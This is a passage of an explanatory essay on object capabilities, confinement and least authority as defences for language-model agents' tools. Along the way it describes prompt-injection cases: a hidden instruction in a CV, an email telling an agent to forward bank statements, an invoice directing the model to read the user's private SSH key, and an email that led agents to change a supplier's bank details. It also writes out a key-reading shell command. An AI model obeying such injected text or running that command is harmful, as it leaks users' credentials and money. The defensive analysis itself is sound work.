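# Object capabilities and least authority for the tools of language-model agents

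## What is a capability, and what do agents run with instead?

In computer security, a capability is an unforgeable reference that both designates a resource, such as a file, and permits certain operations on it. Under the object-capability discipline, a program can act only through references that its creator gave it, that it made itself, or that it received from something it already refers to. The discipline serves the broader principle of least authority, which holds that a component should be able to cause only the effects its task needs. Both ideas come from the design of operating systems and programming languages. Security engineers have recently adopted them for language-model agents, which are programs that let a large language model choose actions and then carry them out on a real computer or account. Most agents that people start on their own machines instead run with the full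 powers of the person who started them.

### The agent loop and prompt injection

Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarise the invoices in one folder. Two pieces of software share the work. The model receives a text prompt and generates text that continues it. The harness is the ordinary program around the model that builds the prompt, reads the model's output and carries out any actions needed on the machine.

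*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the cycle in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness assembles a prompt from general instructions, a list of tools and the user's message. The model's response is either a final answer or a request for a tool call, for example to run `ls` and report the output. The harness executes any requested call, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again. The cycle stops when the model produces a message for the user instead of another request, which can take hundreds of tool calls.

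For the invoices, the calls would list the folder, open the files one by one and save a summary. The model only emits a string such as `cat invoices/0412.txt`, which a process on the user's machine then acts on. Codex's shell tool takes a command, a working directory and a time limit, so the model can use nearly every program on the machine through this one tool. Codex runs the shell tool in a sandbox, but Bolin notes that the sandbox doesn't cover tools from other sources, such as those a user connects through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common interface for plugging tools into agents. Those tools have to supply their own guardrails.

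Outsiders wrote the invoices, and their text enters the same prompt as the user's request. This makes prompt injection possible, in which an attacker puts instructions into data that an agent will read, and the model follows them. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a CV with hidden text that tells a recruiter's model to approve the candidate. In SQL injection, an older attack, text from a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent this by sending the command and the data separately, so that the database engine never runs data as a command. A language model has no such separation. It predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, and David C thinks it quite possible that prompt injection will never have a complete fix. Researchers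 often measure the problem with *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark of 97 tasks and 629 security test cases in which agents work in simulated applications, such as email and banking, and read data that contains injections.

### Ambient authority

An injected instruction can achieve at most what the harness and its tools can do, which on an ordinary computer is a great deal. Gyorffy points out in *Your coding agent has your keys* that the operating system runs a local coding agent, and every shell command, package manager and test runner it starts, as processes under the user's account. Unix file permissions do not distinguish the agent from the person at the terminal. Unless someone adds a sandbox, the invoice assistant can therefore read the user's tax returns and login keys, though its task concerns one folder.

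This is ambient authority, which Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003) define in *Capability Myths Demolished* as authority that a program exercises without selecting it. They compare it to doors that have no keys and open when the right person walks up. With the Unix call `open()`, for example, a program supplies a file name but no credential, and the call succeeds or fails depending on the account the program runs under.

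Programs ran with all of their user's authority long before there were agents. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) uses the card game Solitaire as an example. Solitaire needs a window, the player's clicks and one file for the score, but it can delete any file its user can delete and search the user's mail. People have lived with this for decades, partly because Solitaire does harm only if its author is dishonest or an attacker finds an exploitable bug. An agent can do harm without either, because it may follow instructions that an attacker has put in an invoice it reads.

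Connecting more tools enlarges the pool of authority. As Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* (2026) observes, a client connected to file, database, email and shell servers gives the model the combined authority of all four, so text in an email can trigger a shell command. (Semgrep sells security tools, but the observation follows from how the loop works.) Alpert (2025) argues that companies will do better to issue agents their own credentials, without all the permissions of the people who start them. Separate credentials shrink the pool and are probably worth issuing, but they are only a partial remedy because the method of checking stays the same. The system still accepts the name of any file the agent's account may use, whether the name came from the user or from an invoice.

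### Access lists and capabilities

Textbooks often present access control lists and capabilities as two ways of storing the same table. This table, computer scientist Butler Lampson's access matrix, has a row for each subject (a user or a program), a column for each resource, and the allowed operations in the cells. An access control list is a column, kept with the resource, that records who may do what to it. A capability list is a row, belonging to the subject, that records what that subject may use. *SudoBench* (2026), a benchmark of authorisation in agents, still introduces them this way.

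The row goes back to a 1966 paper by Dennis and Van Horn, two MIT researchers, on computers with many simultaneous users. That paper introduced the word "capability", according to the historical survey *Early Capability Architectures*. In their design, each computation runs inside a "sphere of protection" defined by a list of capabilities. Each entry locates an object and specifies the permitted actions, which for a segment of memory might be reading, reading and writing, or execution. A program uses an entry by giving its position in the list, so it has no way to refer to a segment that isn't listed.

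The textbook equivalence correctly describes who can do what at a given moment, but Miller, Yee and Shapiro argue that it breaks down once a system runs. Two of their reasons matter for agents. In an access-list system, a program designates a file by a name from a shared namespace, and the system separately checks whether the program's account may use that file. A capability combines the designation with the right, so a program that designates a file through a capability also presents the right to use it.

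Their other reason is that the subjects in an access list end up being user accounts, because somebody has to write each subject into the list and nobody can keep it current for processes that live a few seconds. Miller and colleagues knew of no access-list system in which individual processes were separate subjects, whereas capability systems routinely give every running instance its own set of rights. With an access list, an agent session that summarizes invoices and a later one that writes code are the same subject, with the same powers, if both run under the same account.

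Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, make the difference concrete with two Unix commands that copy a file. This is the first:

`cp foo.txt bar.txt`

The shell passes `cp` two strings. To turn them into files, `cp` has to look them up in the user's file system and open them, and since the user could have typed any two names, `cp` must be able to open anything that the user can open. The least authority with which it can do its job is all of the user's authority over files. The other command has the same result:

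`cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`

Here the shell itself opens both files, one for reading and one for writing, and passes `cat` the open files, which Unix calls file descriptors. Unix still runs `cat` with the user's full authority, but the copy would succeed if `cat` had only those two descriptors.

How much authority a program needs thus depends on how its caller tells it what to work on. A shell-using agent works like `cp`: the model emits path names as strings, and the harness resolves them against everything the user owns. Unix already supports both styles, and Miller and Shapiro remark that capability systems differ from it more by removing the `cp` style than by elaborating the `cat` style. The language E, the Unix extension Capsicum and the WebAssembly interface WASI each remove the `cp` style in some form. File descriptors are not quite true capabilities, because an access list governs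 the channel through which one process passes them to another.

### The confused deputy

Excess authority is one problem with separating names from rights. Hardy described another in *The Confused Deputy* (1988), drawing on an incident about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers.

Tymshare kept its Fortran compiler in a directory called SYSX. The compiler collected statistics on how people used the language and wrote them to the file (SYSX)STAT. To allow this, the staff gave the compiler a "home files license", which let it write to files in its own directory. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. The company's billing records were in the same directory, in the file (SYSX)BILL. One day a user entered that name. The compiler asked the operating system to open the file for output, the operating system allowed it because the compiler's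 license covered SYSX, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

Hardy explains why the obvious fixes were inadequate. The compiler could not refuse names in other directories, because users had good reasons to send output there. It could not refuse every name in SYSX, because someone with legitimate access might want a file there. A special check for BILL would protect only one file and need an update whenever staff added another sensitive one. Tymshare did build a system call that let the compiler choose between its own authority and its user's, but some applications needed more than two authorities, and not every authority concerned files. The code for debugging output had been correct until someone added the license. Hardy concludes that the compiler then had authority from two sources and no way to specify which one to use for a given write.

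With capabilities, the staff would give the compiler a reference to the statistics file, and the user would pass it a reference to the output file. The compiler would write statistics through the first reference and debugging output through the second. A user without a reference to the billing file could not direct the debugging output to it.

The same parts turn up in an agent that reads its user's email while holding the user's credentials:

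| Tymshare's compiler | An agent that reads email |
|---|---|
| The compiler | The model and the harness |
| The home files license | The user's logins for mail and files |
| A user with no right to the billing file | A stranger with no right to the user's account |
| The name (SYSX)BILL, typed as an output file | A line in the stranger's email: forward the bank statements to this address |
| The operating system, which finds a valid license | The mail server, which finds a valid login |
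| Lost billing records | Leaked bank statements |

The history carries over too. An agent that only summarises mail may be fairly harmless until someone adds a tool for sending it.

The parallel is looser in one respect, because a model handles the user's request and the stranger's email in one stream of text. Tymshare's compiler had separate pieces of code for its two jobs, and each could have used its own capability without risk of a mix-up. David C therefore calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies, meaning that engineers can repair a classical deputy but can only limit the damage when a model is confused. Semgrep's promise that capabilities mean "no confused deputies" is too strong for this case, since an agent that properly holds both a reference to the bank statements and a reference for sending mail can still combine them at a stranger's request. Miller and colleagues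 made a weaker claim in 2003, that removing ambient authority helps programmers avoid confused deputies but does not guarantee it.

Papers use "confused deputy" differently. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) reserves the term for cases where the agent's legitimate user lacks a permission that the agent has, as when an employee asks an assistant for everybody's salary and the assistant can open the personnel database. That definition excludes the email attack, because the user could have forwarded the statements personally. *SudoBench* reports that surveys list indirect prompt injection (the kind that arrives in data) as a separate class. A wider sense that covers both the salary request and the email attack seems more useful for agents. In both cases, one party supplies the designation and another party's authority makes it work, which was Hardy's complaint.

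### Other things that people call capabilities

AI researchers use "capability" to mean a model's skill, as in "dangerous capabilities", a sense unrelated to references. Linux also has "capabilities", which follow a draft of the POSIX standard for Unix-like systems and split the administrator's power into a fixed set of flags. The flag CAP_CHOWN, for example, lets a process change the owner of any file on the machine. Such a flag doesn't designate a particular file, so it can't limit a process to one folder.

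A third sense causes more trouble because it comes up in discussions of agent security. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) uses "capability gating" to mean choosing which tools a model can call. The paper audits the public code of LangChain/LangGraph and LlamaIndex, two widely used agent frameworks, and of the payment company Stripe's toolkit for agents. All three let a developer choose the tools, but none of them, by default, checks the values in a call against a policy before running it. In a demonstration with a mock payment system, LangChain's normal dispatch let through a tool call that redirected a merchant's payouts to an attacker's account, because the tool existed and the account number had the right format.

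Mellafe Zuvic's remedy is a checkpoint that compares the arguments with a list the operator wrote in advance, and it blocked the same call. A capability design would instead give the agent a payout reference already tied to the merchant's own account, with no account field for the model to fill in.

### Where references come from

In a capability system, a program can act only through references, so the important question is how it can get them. Miller lists four ways, which the invoice assistant can illustrate.

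- **Initial conditions.** The reference already exists when the analysis begins. The harness, say, starts out with access to the user's files.
- **Parenthood.** Whoever creates a thing holds the first and only reference to it. If the assistant creates a scratch file, no other program can reach that file until the assistant shares it.
- **Endowment.** A creator equips its creation with references that the creator already has. The harness starts the assistant with a reference to the invoice folder.
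- **Introduction.** A party that holds references to two others sends one of them a reference to the other. Halfway through the task, the harness might pass the assistant a reference to last year's folder.

The list does not include guessing or looking something up by name. Miller treats plain data, such as numbers and strings, as information that anybody may have if they can work it out, but that gives no access to anything. An assistant that reads the path of the user's private keys in an invoice knows where the keys are but still cannot open them. Two groups of objects with no reference between them can therefore never become connected, because no object can introduce them. All this requires a language or operating system without back doors, which rules out C++ because a C++ program can turn an integer into a pointer.

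For the invoice task, the agent's grant (the set of capabilities it receives) can then contain just two capabilities. The first is a read-only reference to the folder, which the harness makes from its own read-write reference. Capability programmers call this step attenuation. The second lets the agent write a single new file for the summary. The grant includes no shell, mail or network access.

This describes the assistant's permissions, which are what it can do directly. Its authority, which includes every effect it can bring about, may be larger. In Miller and Shapiro's example, Alice has permission to read a password file and Bob doesn't, but Alice can talk to Bob and sends him copies. Bob therefore has authority to read the file without having permission. Similarly, suppose a nightly job on the user's machine emails every new summary to whatever addresses appear in the summary's first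 line. The assistant then has authority to send email to anyone through its permission to write one file.

The classic rule in this area is the principle of least privilege, which Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder set out in 1975. Miller and Shapiro find it unclear whether "privilege" there means permission or authority, and they think the difference is enormous. Permissions are easy to list, but the list for the invoice assistant would not show the nightly job. Authority can't be determined exactly, because it depends on how every program along the way will behave. Miller's compromise, which proofs of confinement also rely on, is to compute an upper bound. The most cautious version assumes that every program passes on whatever it can, and counts everything reachable by any chain of references. An arrangement that passes this test is safe, but the test also rejects many harmless ones.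 Knowing how particular programs behave allows a tighter bound. For instance, if the nightly job mails summaries only to the user, the assistant can no longer write to strangers, though it can still show a wrong total to the person who pays the invoices.

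## How do E, Capsicum and WASI confine a program to what it is handed?

Miller's list of the ways a program can get a reference is complete only if the software underneath the program provides no other way. Ordinary languages and operating systems provide several, including global variables, library functions that open any file, and a directory tree that every process can search. E closes these routes in the programming language, Capsicum in the Unix kernel, and WASI in WebAssembly, a virtual machine that runs programs compiled from many languages. The three differ in how much existing software they can run and in their trusted base, the code and people that must behave correctly for a guarantee to hold.

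### E: confinement inside a language

An E program consists of objects that send each other messages. Each object has code and a private set of references. While it responds to a message, it can use those references, any that arrived with the message, and plain data such as numbers. The disk, the screen and the network are also objects, so an object with no reference to the disk cannot write a file.

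Miller and Shapiro derive capabilities from ordinary object-oriented programming by prohibiting three things it never needed. A program must not turn a number into a pointer (memory safety), and one object must not reach into another's private state (encapsulation). Together, these two rules make references unforgeable. The third prohibition covers global variables whose value can change. If two objects can both use such a variable, one can leave a reference in it for the other to pick up, which connects them without a third object introducing them. Java and Smalltalk allow this and so fall outside the model. E also has no counterpart to Unix's `open()`, which any code can call to reach a file by name.

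Users of E have to trust its implementation, in particular the loader. The loader takes a piece of code and a list of references, creates an object with exactly those references, and returns the only reference to the new object.

### Building narrower powers from wider ones

A reference in E gives full and permanent use of the object it designates. To grant less, a programmer puts a second object in front of the first and hands that one over instead. The simplest is a facet, which passes on only some messages. For the invoice folder it might look like this in pseudocode:

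```
def readOnly(folder):
    return object:
        list()     -> folder.list()
        read(name) -> folder.read(name)
```

The facet keeps `folder` in its private state, so an assistant that holds the facet can read invoices but can't call `folder.write`. The `read` method has to return text, because if it returned a file object with a `write` method, the assistant could use that to change the invoices.

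The caretaker, which dates from work by Redell in 1974, limits a grant in time:

```
def makeCaretaker(target):
    caretaker = object:
        any message m -> target.m     # forward whatever arrives
    revoker = object:
        revoke() -> target = null
    return caretaker, revoker
```

Both objects share the variable `target`. The harness gives the assistant the caretaker and keeps the revoker. The caretaker works just as the folder would until the harness calls `revoke()`, after which every message to the caretaker fails.

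Several researchers have nonetheless written that capability systems can't take back what they have granted. Miller and Shapiro trace the claim to analyses that consider only permissions. In such an analysis, the assistant only ever had permission to use the caretaker, not the folder, and it keeps that permission after the revocation. It has lost its authority to use the folder, but the analysis doesn't cover authority. Considering only permissions also makes audits incomplete. Karger and Herbert proposed in 1984 to give security officers a list of everyone with access to a compromised object, but the list would omit anyone whose access ran through a caretaker.

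A caretaker also covers only the one reference it wraps. Suppose the folder answers a message `open(name)` with a file object. The assistant could open every file early on and keep using the file objects after the harness had revoked the folder. A membrane closes this gap by wrapping every reference that passes through it, in either direction:

```
def makeMembrane(target):
    live = true
    def wrap(x):
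        if x is plain data: return x
        return object:
            any message m(args) ->
                if not live: fail
                return wrap(x.m(wrap each of args))
    revoker = object:
        revoke() -> live = false
    return wrap(target), revoker
```

A call to `open` now returns a wrapped file, calls to that file return wrapped results, and one `revoke()` cuts off access to them all. The arguments need wrapping too, because otherwise the assistant could pass in its own object, and the folder could call that object with an unwrapped reference. Miller presents membranes as a way to form compartments, with the wrapped objects on one side and their users on the other. Plain data passes through unwrapped, so a membrane can't take back an invoice that the assistant has already read.

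Sealers and unsealers, an idea that James Morris published in 1973, hide a reference from the party that carries it:

```
sealer, unsealer = makeSealerPair()
box = sealer.seal(account)
unsealer.unseal(box)              # returns account
```

A payments component could give the invoice assistant a sealed box containing a reference to a supplier's account. The box has no methods, and only the matching unsealer can get the reference out. The assistant could attach the box to the right invoice and send both back to the payments component, but it couldn't move money or look up the balance. The effect resembles public-key encryption but needs no cryptography, because within a single language runtime no object can forge the box or look inside it.

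These patterns limit what a program gets from its user, but the program may arrive with references of its own. In 1973 Lampson posed the confinement problem, in which a customer wants to run somebody else's program on private data without it leaking the data. In Miller and Shapiro's solution, the vendor ships only code, which contains no references, and the customer chooses which references to give it when starting it. A trademark check, which looks for a stamp that only genuine code-only packages carry, assures the customer that the program has no hidden connection to the vendor.

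Miller and Shapiro compare this to buying a pocket calculator and seeing that no wires come out of the case. The guarantee doesn't cover covert channels such as timing, or a calculator on the vendor's website. Likewise, a user can choose which references a downloaded tool starts with, but can't see what a hosted MCP server is connected to.

The same method can make information flow in only one direction. In another of their examples, a customer starts two untrusted programs and gives one an object that stores an integer and the other an object that reads it. According to an older argument, the first program could pass a capability through this channel, and the second could use it to reply. This fails because the storing object accepts only integers. The customer wrote that object in a few lines of code, which enforce the policy on both programs regardless of their size.

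### The powerbox

Under these rules a text editor starts without access to any files, but its user expects to be able to open any document. On an ordinary desktop the Open dialog is part of the editor, which lists the user's files, takes the name the user picks and opens that file with the user's authority. The editor therefore needs all of that authority all the time.

CapDesk, a desktop that Marc Stiegler built in E and that Miller describes, moves the file dialog into a separate trusted component called the powerbox. An editor holds a reference to its powerbox and requests a file through it. The powerbox, which has access to the user's files, displays them. When the user clicks on one, the powerbox gives the editor a reference to only that file.

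The user selects a file as usual, and the click that designates the file also grants access to it, so no permission prompt appears. The program receives the file as `cat` does, except that the user chooses it with a mouse instead of in a shell. Miller calls CapDesk "virus-safe", but that depends on the powerbox and E having no security holes, and reviewers did find some in E.

### What Joe-E took out of Java

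E required programmers to learn a new language. In *Joe-E*, Mettler, Wagner and Close started from Java and removed whatever broke the object-capability discipline. A Joe-E program is an ordinary Java program that also passes a verifier, which checks each source file separately without changing it.

| What Joe-E removes or restricts | What a program could otherwise do with it |
|---|---|
| Native methods | Run code from outside Java, which can forge references |
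| Static fields that can change | Exchange references through a global variable |
| Library calls that reach files or the network by name | Use the authority of the whole process |
| Reflection that ignores `private` | Take a reference out of another object |
| Exceptions that contain mutable objects | Leak a reference to a distant caller |
| Custom `finalize()` methods | Revive an object that its own constructor had rejected |
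| `finally` blocks, and catching errors such as memory exhaustion | Make another object fail halfway through an update, then exploit its inconsistent state |

Exceptions in Java can leak private references. If a component lends such a reference to a helper, the helper can throw an exception that contains it. Unless the component catches the exception, both the exception and the reference reach the component's caller. A reviewer who read only the component's own code would miss the leak.

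The restriction on library calls is the hardest to get right. Mettler and colleagues went through Java's library and allowed only the methods that respect the discipline, a process they call taming. They disallowed the constructor that turns a string into a file, as well as `getParentFile()`, which would let a program with one file climb to the root directory. Joe-E also replaces the constructor `File(dir, child)`, which appears to narrow access from a folder to a file inside it, with a wrapper that rejects a null `dir`. When `dir` is null, Java treats `child` as a path that can start from the root.

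Each of these decisions becomes part of the trusted base. E's designers had to make similar decisions. A security review of the DarpaBrowser, a web browser built on E, found that E's list allowed some methods that break capability discipline. Mettler and colleagues consider taming a substantial weakness of their approach and accept that their list may contain mistakes. Users also have to trust any ordinary Java code in the same application. Joe-E doesn't limit processor time or memory, so untrusted code can still hang the program.

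A reviewer can answer some questions about a component from its interface alone, without reading its code. Suppose an image viewer accepts decoders from strangers, on condition that each decoder is immutable and has a single method that takes bytes and returns a bitmap. A malicious decoder could show the wrong picture, but it couldn't write a file, send a packet or remember anything about one image while decoding the next.

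### Capsicum: confinement in the Unix kernel

Mettler and colleagues meant Joe-E for new code, and neither it nor E can do much to confine the C programs that an agent starts from a shell. Watson, Anderson and colleagues' *Capsicum* (2010) enforces the limits in the kernel of FreeBSD, a Unix system, so that an existing program can give up its ambient authority and keep only chosen file descriptors.

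A file descriptor is already close to a capability. The process has only a small integer, say 4, which the kernel looks up in that process's own table. The process can make up other integers, but each refers either to something it already holds or to nothing.

A process gives up its other powers with the system call `cap_enter`, which switches it to capability mode. No later call can undo this, and child processes inherit it. The kernel then blocks access to namespaces shared by the whole machine. Watson and colleagues list eleven of these in FreeBSD, including file paths, process numbers, network addresses and system clocks. A program can normally query some 3,000 system settings through one interface, but only about 30 stay available in capability mode.

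Plain descriptors still grant too much authority. For example, Unix lets a process change a file's permissions through a descriptor it opened only for reading. Capsicum can therefore wrap a descriptor in a mask of about 60 possible rights, such as read, write and seek. Wrapping it again can remove rights but never add any, which is the kernel's version of attenuation. Capsicum checks these rights in the single function that turns descriptor numbers into files, so the designers had to implement the check correctly in only one place.

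A program that needs a whole directory can hold a descriptor for it and use `openat` to look up names relative to that directory. If descriptor 4 refers to `/lib`, then `openat(4, "libc.so.7")` succeeds, while `openat(4, "../etc/passwd")` and `openat(4, "/etc/passwd")` both fail. Capsicum rejects every path that contains `..`, even a harmless one, because two cooperating processes could otherwise rearrange the directories during a lookup and escape.

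Programs that need new files at unpredictable moments have to be split into two processes. One keeps the user's authority and opens files, and the other, a helper in capability mode, does the risky work with the descriptors it receives over a socket. A library starts the helper with clean memory and closes every descriptor that the program hasn't explicitly passed on. The first process can be a powerbox. Watson and colleagues found delegation most valuable in windowing systems, where a user's click or drag can trigger it.

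They converted four programs:

| Program | Lines of code | What runs in capability mode |
|---|---|---|
| `tcpdump`, which displays network traffic | 2, or about 10 with limits on the terminal | The loop that parses packets |
| `dhclient`, which obtains a network address | 2 | The part that already ran with reduced privileges |
| `gzip`, which compresses files | 409, about 16% of the program | A helper with one input and one output descriptor |
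| Chromium, the web browser | About 100 | The processes that render pages |

Chromium used other sandboxes on other systems. The Windows sandbox took 22,350 lines of code and still let a confined process contact servers on the internet. One Linux sandbox took 11,301 lines, and another, with a looser policy, took only 200. Capsicum took a hundred, partly because Chromium's developers had already split the browser into processes that pass descriptors to each other. `gzip` is a better indication of how much work Capsicum requires for a program without such a split.

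The line counts also leave out the debugging. After the two-line change, `tcpdump` could no longer turn network addresses into names, because the C library doesn't read its configuration file until the first lookup, and by then the process couldn't open files. The confined `gzip` ran unexpectedly faster than the original because a global variable holding the compression level had never reached the helper, which therefore compressed at the wrong level. Watson and colleagues conclude that the largest problem with Capsicum and its relatives is that programming this way is difficult.

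Running time is a much smaller concern. On the test machine, each operation on a wrapped descriptor took about 0.06 microseconds longer, an increase of 10% in the worst case, which was a call that did almost no work. Entering capability mode took 1.2 microseconds. Creating a helper, exchanging one message with it and shutting it down took about 1.5 milliseconds. The confined `gzip` took an extra 2.4 milliseconds per run regardless of file size, and by about 512 kilobytes the two versions' times were within 5% of each other. These delays are negligible for an agent that waits seconds for each response from its model.

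Capsicum's large trusted base includes the FreeBSD kernel, then 3.8 million lines of C. seL4, a far smaller capability kernel, has computer-checked proofs of its isolation. Capsicum's trusted base also includes the code a program runs before it calls `cap_enter`, because the process keeps its memory and every descriptor it had open. The converted `dhclient`, for instance, could still write arbitrary messages to the system log.

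### WebAssembly and WASI

Compilers can translate C, Rust, Go and many other languages into WebAssembly, an instruction format. A runtime executes the result, gives each module its own block of memory, and checks every access so that the module can't read or write outside that block. A C++ program compiled this way can still turn an integer into a pointer, but the pointer is only a position in the module's own block. Languages that fail Miller's test can therefore run under the discipline, but only if the whole module is confined as a unit, because nothing separates one part of a C++ module from another.

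A WebAssembly module affects the outside world through imports, which are functions that the host program supplies when it starts the module. According to *Security model*, the documentation for a small WebAssembly runtime, a module has no other way to affect the outside world, so one that receives no imports can only compute. WASI, the WebAssembly System Interface, is a standard set of imports for files, clocks, network connections and the like. Its versions grant access somewhat differently, as WASI's *Security* page explains.

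In WASI 0.1, the host opens certain directories before the program starts and passes it their descriptors. The program can open files beneath these preopened directories, much as with Capsicum's `openat`, but it has no call for requesting other directories.

WASI 0.2 added components, which are modules with typed interfaces. A component declares each kind of access it needs as a separate import, so anyone can check the file before running it to see whether it imports network access. The imports show only the kind of access, and the host still determines which folders the component can use by opening them for it. Components also use typed handles to refer to particular resources, such as an open file. A component can't make up a handle and has to receive one from the host or another component.

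WASI 0.3.0 came out on June 11, 2026, and in late November WASI's *Releases* page listed 0.3 as the current stable version. Most compilers and related tools still targeted 0.2, and many production systems still used 0.1. Components built for 0.2 also run on runtimes that support 0.3. On August 6 the standards group adopted further features for 0.3.1. Version 1.0 has no date because the groups responsible haven't yet defined what it requires. Most of what is new in 0.3 concerns concurrency, and *The Async Component Model* (Bratschi-Kaye, 2026) explains it from a compiler writer's point of view.

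In WASI 0.3, data can flow between components through typed streams. *WASI 0.3*, published by the Bytecode Alliance, the industry group that develops the Wasmtime runtime, describes each stream as a handle with an owner. A component that passes a stream to another component loses access to it. In E, the sender would keep its own reference, so both objects would have access.

The other change loosens control over network access. In 0.2, a program had to supply a network handle to connect to a server or look up a host name, so programmers could pass the handle to one component and withhold it from another. In 0.3, the host grants network access to a component as a whole, and any code in it can connect without a handle. Inside a component with network access, the network is now ambient in Miller, Yee and Shapiro's sense. According to WASI's security page, code under WASI has no ambient authority,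 but that is accurate only for the boundary between component and host.

To keep a library off the network, a developer has to put it in its own component. Alternatively, a second component can implement the network functions and forward only calls to approved servers. This is the facet pattern again, with components in place of objects.

According to the same page, WASI's sandboxing is stronger than typical isolation between operating system processes. This depends on the runtime. Bytecode Alliance's *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (2026) covers 12 advisories for one runtime, Wasmtime, all published on the same day. That was three times as many as in all of 2025, and came after language-model tools had found 11 of the flaws within three weeks. Two of the flaws were critical and could let a program escape from the sandbox. Three others were in the code that passes strings between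 components.

One of the critical flaws was in compiler rules that researchers had formally verified. A later release changed the rules without a matching update to the formal model, and once the team updated the model, verification found the same bug. Neither escape affected Wasmtime's main compiler on x86-64 processors, which is the most common configuration. Still, anyone who relies on WASI has to include a compiler in the trusted base and install its updates.

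### An invoice tool as a component

Developers have begun to ship agent tools as WebAssembly components. Microsoft's *Introducing Wassette* (2025) presents a runtime, built on Wasmtime, that lets agents use these components as MCP tools. An agent can fetch a component from a container image registry, and the component has no access to the system until somebody grants it. McDonald (2025), in *Build MCP Servers with Wasmcp and Spin*, describes a kit for building whole MCP servers from components, including shared ones for authorisation and logging.

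Both routes take work, because the code has to compile to a component. Microsoft's *What is Wassette?* acknowledges that developers would need to rewrite existing MCP servers. Wassette was still an early project when version 0.4.0 came out in February 2026. Gitpedia's *Wassette* page repeats the developers' warning that Wassette isn't ready for production.

Wassette grants access through a policy file. For a component that summarises invoices, the part about files could look like this, where `summary` is a new, empty folder:

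```
allow:
  - uri: "fs://invoices/**"
    access: ["read"]
  - uri: "fs://summary/**"
    access: ["read", "write"]
```

The policy has no entry for the network. It is a list of path names, so on paper it resembles an access control list. The difference comes when the host turns those names into preopened directories for one running component:

1. The host, which runs with the user's authority, opens the two folders and starts the component with a descriptor for each.
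2. The model requests a call to the summarising tool with the file name `0412.txt`. The harness passes this string on to the component.
3. The component looks up `0412.txt` relative to its descriptor for `invoices`. The lookup succeeds, and the component reads the file and writes a summary to the other folder.
4. The invoice contains an injected instruction to summarise `../.ssh/id_ed25519`, the user's private login key. The model complies and requests another call with that path.
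5. The component attempts the lookup from the same descriptor. The path leads out of the folder, so the runtime returns an error. The user's account may read the key, but that makes no difference, because the component holds no descriptor from which to reach it.

The result would be the same if the component's author were malicious. The component could write a false summary, but it could not open the key or send the invoices over the network.

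This confinement applies only to the component, which may be one of several tools the agent has. If the harness also gives the model an ordinary shell, the injected instruction could lead the model to run `cat ~/.ssh/id_ed25519` there, and the invoice tool's policy would not restrict that call.

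## What can be proved about programs that hold only capabilities?

One unrestricted shell can undo a careful policy elsewhere, so determining what a program can do requires looking at everything it holds and everything those things hold in turn. Capability researchers represent these relationships as a graph and prove which changes to it are possible.

### The reference graph

Every component of the system, whether a program, a file or a device, is a node. An arrow runs from one node to another if the first holds a reference to the second. In the model that Miller and Shapiro set out, Miller's ways of getting a reference become two rules for adding arrows, and a third rule removes them:

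1. Introduction: a node with arrows to two others can give one of them an arrow to the other. It can also send a reference to itself.
2. Parenthood and endowment: a node that creates another gets an arrow to it and can give it copies of its own arrows.
3. Discarding: a node can drop a reference, which removes an arrow.

Two nodes are connected if a path of arrows joins them, whichever way the arrows point. The basic theorem is that two parts of the graph that start unconnected stay unconnected.

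The proof is by induction on the number of steps. Suppose the two parts are unconnected before a given step. If node u sends v a reference to w, then u already had arrows to both, so v and w were in the same part and the new arrow stays inside it. If u creates a node, all the new node's arrows lead to or from u's part. Discarding a reference only removes an arrow, so it can't join the parts. The parts are therefore still unconnected after the step. Miller and Shapiro describe this as "only connectivity begets connectivity".

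We can ignore which way the arrows point because references can travel in both directions. A node with an arrow to the assistant can send it any reference the node holds, even if the assistant has no arrow back. Miller and Shapiro treat a call and its reply as two messages, so a caller that expects an answer has to supply a reference for the reply. The component it called can then send references back with the answer.

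Here is a system with five nodes:

```
assistant -> invoices
assistant -> converter
converter -> mail
keys
```

The converter is a tool that turns scanned invoices into text. It has a reference to the mail sender so that it can report crashes to its developer. The user's login keys have no arrows to or from anything else here. The system might run like this:

| Step | New arrow |
|---|---|
| The assistant sends the converter a scan, with a reference to itself for the reply | converter → assistant |
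| The converter replies with the text and a reference to the mail sender | assistant → mail |
| The assistant sends the converter a reference to the invoice folder | converter → invoices |

The assistant can now send email, although its original grant contained only the folder and the converter. After three steps, both programs hold everything that either held at the start. The theorem allows this because all four nodes were connected. But it rules out any arrow to the keys, because only a node that already had one could pass it on.

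Now suppose the harness puts a wrapper that forwards only text between the assistant and the converter. The converter can no longer pass the mail sender to the assistant. But the assistant may still be able to cause emails by sending text that makes the converter report a crash. The wrapper has reduced what the assistant may do directly, but the assistant's authority still includes causing some emails to be sent.

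Removing that authority requires a wrapper that completely blocks communication in one direction. The harness could give the invoice folder to the converter instead of the assistant, let the converter write text into the wrapper, and let the assistant only read that text. Nothing the assistant does would then affect the mail sender, though the converter could still influence the assistant.

The connectivity test doesn't detect this improvement, because a path of arrows still runs through the wrapper. Miller and Shapiro call such a worst-case bound "arrangement-only". They call the tighter kind, which uses knowledge of the wrapper's code, "partially behavioural". These ideas were informal until *Permission and Authority Revisited* (Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues, 2016) proposed definitions of permission, authority and their bounds in a small object-oriented calculus.

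*Taming AI Agents with seL4* (Alhindi, 2026) applies a similar test to text instead of references. The test case is a team of five agents that processes suppliers' invoices on the seL4 kernel. Alhindi draws an edge from one agent to another if the first can write to memory or a tool that the second reads from. Only one agent reads email, and no agent combines untrusted input, private data and the power to change something. But Alhindi followed the edges and found that text from an email could reach the other four agents, all of which could see private data and make changes.

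When Alhindi sent the team a malicious email, its hidden note reached the coordinating agent in 23 of 40 runs, and in 7 of those the coordinator changed the supplier's bank details. Alhindi then replaced the email agent with an ordinary parser that returns only the invoice number, order number, total and supplier. In another 40 runs, no part of the note reached any agent. Alhindi tested only one team and one email, so we can't infer much about other systems from these rates. The parser's success is easier to generalise because it works as a wrapper that drops everything except those four fields.

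### Three properties

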